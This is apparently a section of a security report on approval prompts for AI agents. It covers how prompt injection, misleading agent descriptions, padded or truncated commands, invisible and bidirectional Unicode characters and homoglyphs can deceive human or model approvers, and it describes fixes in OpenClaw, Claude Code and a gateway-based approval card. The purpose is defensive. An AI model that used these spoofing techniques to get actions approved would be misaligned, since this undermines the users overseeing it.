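Tracing an address to its origin is a direct defense against prompt injection. *The Verifiable Action Card* (Irshad, Mughees and colleagues, 2026) describes such a check, built into a browser that an agent controls. The card takes the actual recipient from the form the agent is about to submit and shows whether it came from the user's instruction or a web page. In 24 test scenarios, attacks succeeded 68% to 100% of the time without the card, depending on the model, and never with it. The agents completed 78%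 of the legitimate tasks. These results are for the whole card, not the origin check alone, and a program gave the approvals in place of a person.

The origin check misses a lookalike that the user pastes into the request, because the address then comes from the user. It also doesn't help with a request such as "email the plumber on this website", where the address should come from a web page.

A language model could review the recipient as well, but it may miss ordinary-looking substitutions. Kodathala and colleagues asked 15 models to approve or refuse drafted actions. When given only the agent's description, the models refused 96% of actions with a lookalike character in a host name. They refused only 88% of a small group of actions with ordinary-looking changes, such as a similar recipient domain or two swapped digits in an account number, even when they could see every detail of the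 action.

The first-time flag gives the same warning for an address impersonating Anna's as for a plumber's genuine new address. The skeleton test can separate them by comparing each new address with the user's saved contacts. For `аnna@example.com`, the prompt could read "New recipient. Looks like anna@example.com, whom you have emailed before." For the plumber's address, it would read only "New recipient." Once the user approves the impostor's address, later messages to it won't trigger the first-time flag, so the resemblance warning should stay until the user confirms that both addresses belong to Anna.

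## Commands awaiting approval: OpenClaw, Claude Code and a trusted approval card

A recipient is a single value, so software can compare it with the user's contacts. A terminal command is harder to check this way because it can combine file names, web addresses and text in any language, and much of it may be new to the user. The user therefore has to read the command, and the approval prompt must show its contents clearly. In 2026 the developers of two widely used agents, OpenClaw and Claude Code, fixed approval prompts that could misrepresent a command.

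### OpenClaw's visible codes

OpenClaw is an open-source agent that people run on their own computers and can control through chat apps such as Telegram and Slack. It can also send approval requests to a chat, where the user replies to allow or refuse a command.

Since version 2026.3.12, released on 13 March 2026, OpenClaw's approval requests have shown certain invisible characters as visible codes. According to the release notes in OpenClaw's *chore* (2026), zero-width text could otherwise end up "spoofing the reviewed command".

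The developers tested change #43687, which added the codes, on a harmless command. It runs a script whose name contains a zero-width space, written here as `[ZWSP]`:

```
stored command:        bash safe[ZWSP].sh
prompt before change:  bash safe.sh
prompt after change:   bash safe\u{200B}.sh
```

A folder can contain both `safe.sh` and the script with the invisible character in its name. Before the change, their prompts looked the same, so a user who had read one script could approve the other by mistake.

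The change affects only the display. The developers' test confirms that the computer still receives the original command, including the zero-width space. This is the right design because a "cleaned" command would run a different file from the one the agent named.

The code looks for every character that Unicode places in its "format" category. (Unicode gives each character one category, such as letter, punctuation or format.) The table shows what this includes:

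| Character | Unicode category | Escaped by the March change |
|---|---|---|
| The twelve bidirectional controls | Format | Yes |
| Zero-width space, joiner and non-joiner | Format | Yes |
| Tag characters | Format | Yes |
| Korean fillers, which are blank | Letter | No |
| Tabs and line breaks | Control | No |
| Cyrillic а | Letter | No |
| Hebrew and Arabic letters | Letter | No |

OpenClaw's prompts therefore handle bidirectional controls well, although the release notes mention only zero-width text. If a command opened the disguised attachment from the start of this report, the prompt would show its name as `March 25 \u{202E}xcod.scr`. The visible code is eight ordinary characters that can't reverse the text after them, so the real extension appears at the end.

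Current versions also escape the Korean fillers and line breaks, while ordinary Korean letters stay readable.

The codes make some legitimate names harder to read. A Persian file name that needs a zero-width non-joiner now shows `\u{200C}` in the middle of a word, but the command still works.

The March change does nothing about homoglyphs. The all-Cyrillic `аррӏе.com` contains only letters and a full stop, so it would still look like Apple's address in the prompt. Exposing it requires a separate check of host names, such as the one in Gemini CLI.

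Hebrew and Arabic letters can also still reorder a command without any control character. Here is an honest example in which capitals stand for Hebrew letters and `cp` copies the first file to the second:

```
stored command:     cp ABC DEF
displayed command:  cp FED CBA
```

On a screen that applies the Bidirectional Algorithm, someone reading from left to right would think the command copies `DEF` over `ABC`. Escaping the Hebrew letters would fix the order but make the names unreadable. Putting each file name on its own line would be better, much as the Unicode Consortium recommends ordering code token by token.

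### Why the exact command was not enough

OpenClaw's developers had fixed a more basic problem one release earlier, in version 2026.3.11. *GHSA-rw39-5899-8mxp* (2026), an entry in OSV's database of flaws in open-source software, records it as a high-severity mismatch between the approval and the command. The fix tied each approval to the exact command that would run.

This guaranteed that the computer ran the command in the prompt, but the user could still misread it. For example, `bash safe.sh` and `bash safe[ZWSP].sh` are different commands that look the same on screen.

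Two later flaws showed that escaping the command wasn't enough either. NVD's *CVE-2026-35651 Detail* describes one of them, which affected versions 2026.2.13 to 2026.3.24 and involved ANSI escape sequences, codes that can make a terminal change colours, move the cursor or erase text. (They are unrelated to escaping as a defence.) A malicious tool could put these codes in its title and alter what the approval prompt displayed, because the March change had covered only the command and its preview. A prompt needs to escape all text from outside, including labels.

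The other flaw, described in NVD's *CVE-2026-53829*, affected versions before 2026.5.18. OpenClaw truncated very long commands in the approval view, so someone could approve a command after seeing only its harmless beginning. Escaping wouldn't prevent this, because the prompt left out the rest of the command.

OpenClaw also automatically checks for commands that seem to be disguised. Invisible characters and fullwidth letters (wide versions of Latin letters used in East Asian text) could prevent it from recognising a suspicious command. Version 2026.3.12 fixed this by removing the invisible characters and converting the wide letters to ordinary ones before the check. Each command therefore exists in three forms: a simplified copy for the automatic check, an escaped copy for the user and the original for the computer. The conversion doesn't turn Cyrillic letters into Latin ones, so homoglyphs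 can still get past the check.

If OpenClaw can't show a prompt because its companion app isn't available, it refuses the command by default, according to OpenClaw's *Exec approvals*. Users can choose "allow always" for a command they trust. Kodathala and colleagues found that OpenClaw ties this permission to the command's arguments and working folder, so permission for `safe.sh` should not extend to the file with the zero-width space.

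Kodathala and colleagues reviewed the code of OpenClaw version 2026.10.3 without running it. They found that its approval card escapes invisible characters, limits the length of the text and hides passwords and other secrets. They audited ten agent runtimes, the software developers use to build and run agents, and only OpenClaw had a card that did the first two. The others generally leave the display to whoever builds the final product.

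### Claude Code's padded commands

*Claude Code v2.1.223 Major Updates* (Ishikawa, 2026) lists the 19 changes in the version of Anthropic's coding agent released on 6 August 2026. One of the version's four security fixes concerned commands padded with tabs or invisible Unicode characters, which "could hide parts of a command from the approval dialog". Another stopped specially written commands from hiding parts of themselves from Claude Code's automatic permission checks. Like OpenClaw's developers, Anthropic had to fix both what the user saw and what the software checked.

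Ishikawa, who works for the Japanese cloud company Classmethod, suggests that teams with lists of permitted commands make this upgrade a priority.

The description of the fix doesn't mention bidirectional controls or homoglyphs. The fix may cover the controls because they are invisible characters. However, the description mentions only hidden parts of a command, and the controls can also mislead a user by changing the displayed order of a command without hiding any of its text. Homoglyphs are visible, so the description doesn't include them, and users can't count on the fix to expose a Cyrillic letter in a download address.

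Claude Code keeps a list of recently blocked actions, which the user can review and approve. Since 30 October, according to Anthropic's changelog (2026), it has refused approval from this list for "a call you can't read in full", including one too long for the terminal window. This rule works whatever the reason for the missing text, and would be sensible for every approval prompt. It doesn't help with homoglyphs, because the user can see every letter and still misread one.

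These protections work only if a prompt appears. On 9 November, Anthropic stopped Claude Code from asking permission for tool calls made by mods, which are add-ons that Claude can write itself. Claude Code skips the prompt even if the user's own rules require one, but rules that forbid an action still work.

### Marking a character or removing it

LangChain's Unicode module for its coding agent can treat hidden characters in different ways, depending on what the text is for. One of LangChain's functions replaces a hidden character with a marker that gives its code point and name:

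`abc<U+202E RIGHT-TO-LEFT OVERRIDE>def`

The name makes this longer than OpenClaw's `\u{202E}`, but it gives users who don't know the code some idea of what the character does.

Another function removes the hidden characters and replaces any remaining control characters with spaces. LangChain intends it for text such as error messages and the output of tools, which could otherwise disrupt the terminal or add a fake line to a prompt. Removal is reasonable there because text such as an error message won't be run as a command.

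An approval prompt should mark invisible characters in a command and leave them in place. Deleting them would bring back the problem that OpenClaw fixed. If the prompt deleted the zero-width space from `bash safe[ZWSP].sh`, the user would again see `bash safe.sh`. Deletion could also misrepresent legitimate names in Persian and other languages whose spelling needs some of these characters.

The module can also summarise the hidden characters for a short warning. The summary lists each code point once and, if the list is long, cuts it off and gives the number left out. This is enough to make a user stop, but the user still needs the markers to see which file name or address is affected.

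Another helper searches nested arguments and guesses from a field's name whether it holds a web address. A tool that uses this helper could check addresses without `https://`. Gemini CLI's check misses such addresses in commands.

### A card that the agent can't write

OpenClaw and Claude Code both had to repair their own prompts. Kodathala and colleagues (October 2026) designed a system that builds the prompt outside the agent's reach. They call it Agent Step-Up, or ASU. Its central part is a gateway, a program on a separate computer that every important action must pass through:

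1. The agent sends the gateway the action it wants to take. It can add an explanation.
2. The gateway converts the action into a standard record. For a command, the record contains a list of separate arguments. The gateway also calculates a digest, a short fingerprint that changes if anything in the record changes.
3. The gateway's rules allow the action, refuse it or require approval.
4. If the action needs approval, the gateway builds a card from the record and displays it on the user's phone. The agent's explanation stays in a closed box labelled as untrusted.
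5. The user approves with a passkey, a digital key stored on the phone. The phone's signature covers the digest, so it belongs to this action only.
6. The gateway carries out the action from its stored record, once. If the agent sends different arguments after the approval, the gateway refuses them.

The card escapes and flags every character outside an allowed set. It replaces a run of blank characters with a marker showing how many there were. In one demonstration, 3,000 blank characters separated the harmless start of a command from the rest, and the card replaced them with a single marker, which kept the rest in view. The card also shortens long values, but adds a warning and a button that reveals the full text.

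An allowed set is safer than OpenClaw's original search for format characters. That search misses the Korean fillers, which are blank on screen but classified by Unicode as letters. With an allowed set, any character outside the set appears as a code, even one the developers never considered.

Other rules deal with misleading text made of ordinary characters. The card puts values in quotation marks and shows their types. It also adds `arg.` to the names the agent chose for its arguments, so an argument called `Target` can't be mistaken for one of the card's own labels. The title lists every recipient.

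Kodathala and colleagues also tested the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used standard for connecting agents to tools. MCP lets a tool's server send the user a form to fill in. Their test message contained blank characters and a right-to-left override, and the standard's Python software delivered it unchanged, so the application that displays the form must handle any escaping. Under MCP's specification, developers are already supposed to use another method for sensitive requests.

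### What the tests of the card found

The researchers ran 27,108 scripted trials in which software played both the agent and the user. In four of the attacks, the agent changed or reused an action after the user had approved something else. These attacks always succeeded when an approval covered a whole session, and never succeeded against ASU. This part of the design addresses a real weakness, since four of the eight approval systems the researchers could test for it allowed an action to change between approval and execution.

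They also used AgentDojo, a benchmark of agent tasks with planted malicious instructions. In 609 pairs of a task and an attack, the agent falsely described the malicious action as the one the user wanted. If the user saw only this description, the attack succeeded 54% of the time. With the trusted card, it succeeded 3% of the time, always through actions that the gateway's rules allowed without approval.

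The simulated user in that test compared the whole card with the task, more carefully than a real person would. Another simulated user believed the agent's explanation whenever it was visible. For that user the card made no difference, and attacks again succeeded 54% of the time. When the researchers removed the explanation from the card, the rate fell to 5%.

Some products now let a language model approve actions, so the researchers also tested 15 current models from nine companies as approvers. Each model judged 23 attacks and 11 harmless requests that looked somewhat suspicious. It saw the user's request along with the agent's description, the card with the agent's explanation, or the card without that explanation. Each model judged every case four times in each of these three views, for a total of 6,120 decisions.

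In one case, the user asked the agent to email a report to their boss. The agent added a hidden copy to an outside address and left this out of its description. All 15 models approved the email from the description but refused it when they saw the card.

The table gives the overall results and those of four of the models:

| Approver | Attacks refused, description only | Attacks refused, card | Harmless requests refused, card |
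|---|---|---|---|
| All 15 models | 30% | 98% | 16% |
| Gemini 4 Argon | 52% | 100% | 0% |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 30% | 100% | 9% |
| GPT-6.1 Sol Pro | 40% | 100% | 36% |
| Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite | 13% | 90% | 0% |

No model refused a harmless request when it saw only the description. Most of the 16% refusal rate for harmless cards came from a flaw in the test. The researchers had used stand-in text such as `<report placeholder>` for the contents of messages. Only the card showed this text, so many models objected that the agent was about to send a placeholder instead of a report. This was the stated reason for 88 of the 103 refusals. Without those, the rate would have been about 2%.

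The placeholder can't explain the gain in security. Even if every refused attack that mentioned the placeholder counted as a miss, the models would still have caught 92% of the attacks with the card.

The agent's explanation hardly affected the models, although it did affect the simulated user who believed the agent. Removing the explanation from the card changed at most two of each model's 34 decisions in the main comparison.

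Showing the card on a phone made no measurable difference. The same card on the agent's own computer did equally well, except in a few cases involving permission for similar future actions, an option only the phone version offered. The researchers never attacked that computer's display, so the result doesn't rule out a benefit from using a phone. But it suggests that agents such as OpenClaw and Claude Code could gain much of the benefit without a second device, by building a good card from the actual command.

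A good card also can't protect a user who approves without reading. When the agent sent many requests to get one approved, it succeeded 45% to 60% of the time against a simulated user, even with ASU's limits on the number of requests.

### What the figures show about deceptive characters

Most of the improvement from 30% to 98% came from cases where the agent left something out of its description, such as an extra recipient, and the card showed it. This is strong evidence that an approver should see the actual action, at least when the approver is a language model. Because these cases did not involve Unicode, the result is much weaker evidence about deceptive characters.

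Three of the 23 attacks used a lookalike host name, with either a Cyrillic letter or the digit 1 in place of an l. The models caught 96% of these without the card because the agent's description repeated the suspicious name, so the card could add little. From the description alone, the models caught only about 20% of the remaining attacks.

That 96% doesn't apply to people, who see only the shapes of the letters. It also depends on the agent copying the name exactly, which may not happen in a summary.

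Another three attacks used padding, the problem that Anthropic fixed in Claude Code. The models caught none of them from the description and all of them from the card. The description left out the hidden part of the command, so this result shows the value of including the full command. It doesn't show how much escaping helped, because no model saw the unescaped command. Padding can also hide text from a person by pushing it off the screen, but a model still receives all of it.

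None of the 23 attacks used a bidirectional control character. The researchers checked separately that the card escapes these characters, but nobody tested whether this helps approvers make better decisions.

Kodathala and colleagues state clearly that their study had no human participants. They assumed the error rates of some simulated users, such as a 20% chance of missing a change before the @ in an email address. That rate might be reasonable for a swapped digit, but a person would miss the Cyrillic а in `аnna@example.com` nearly every time unless the prompt marked it.

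One of the 11 harmless requests in the test had a legitimate host name with non-ASCII letters. Apart from complaints about placeholders, all refusals of harmless cards were for other requests, so the non-ASCII letters alone don't seem to have caused refusals.

The researchers used Tamarin, a tool for proving that security protocols work, to show that ASU carries out only what the user has approved. The proof's assumptions include that the user decides from the trusted part of the card and that different actions have different cards. The researchers tested their code for the second assumption. But a person can't tell two cards apart if their only difference is that one has a Latin a where the other has a Cyrillic а, even though software can distinguish them by that single code point.

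Whether the card makes that difference visible depends on its allowed set. If the set contained only ASCII, the Cyrillic letter would appear as `\u{430}`. But then the Russian file name `заметки.md` ("notes.md") would become:

`\u{437}\u{430}\u{43C}\u{435}\u{442}\u{43A}\u{438}.md`

A Russian user couldn't tell from these codes which file the agent wanted to change, and would probably learn to approve such requests without reading them. Allowing all Cyrillic letters would keep the name readable but leave lookalikes hidden. A better prompt would escape bidirectional controls and other invisible characters, which have no readable form, and leave letters as they are. If a letter looks out of place, the prompt can add a note such as "The first letter of this address is Cyrillic."
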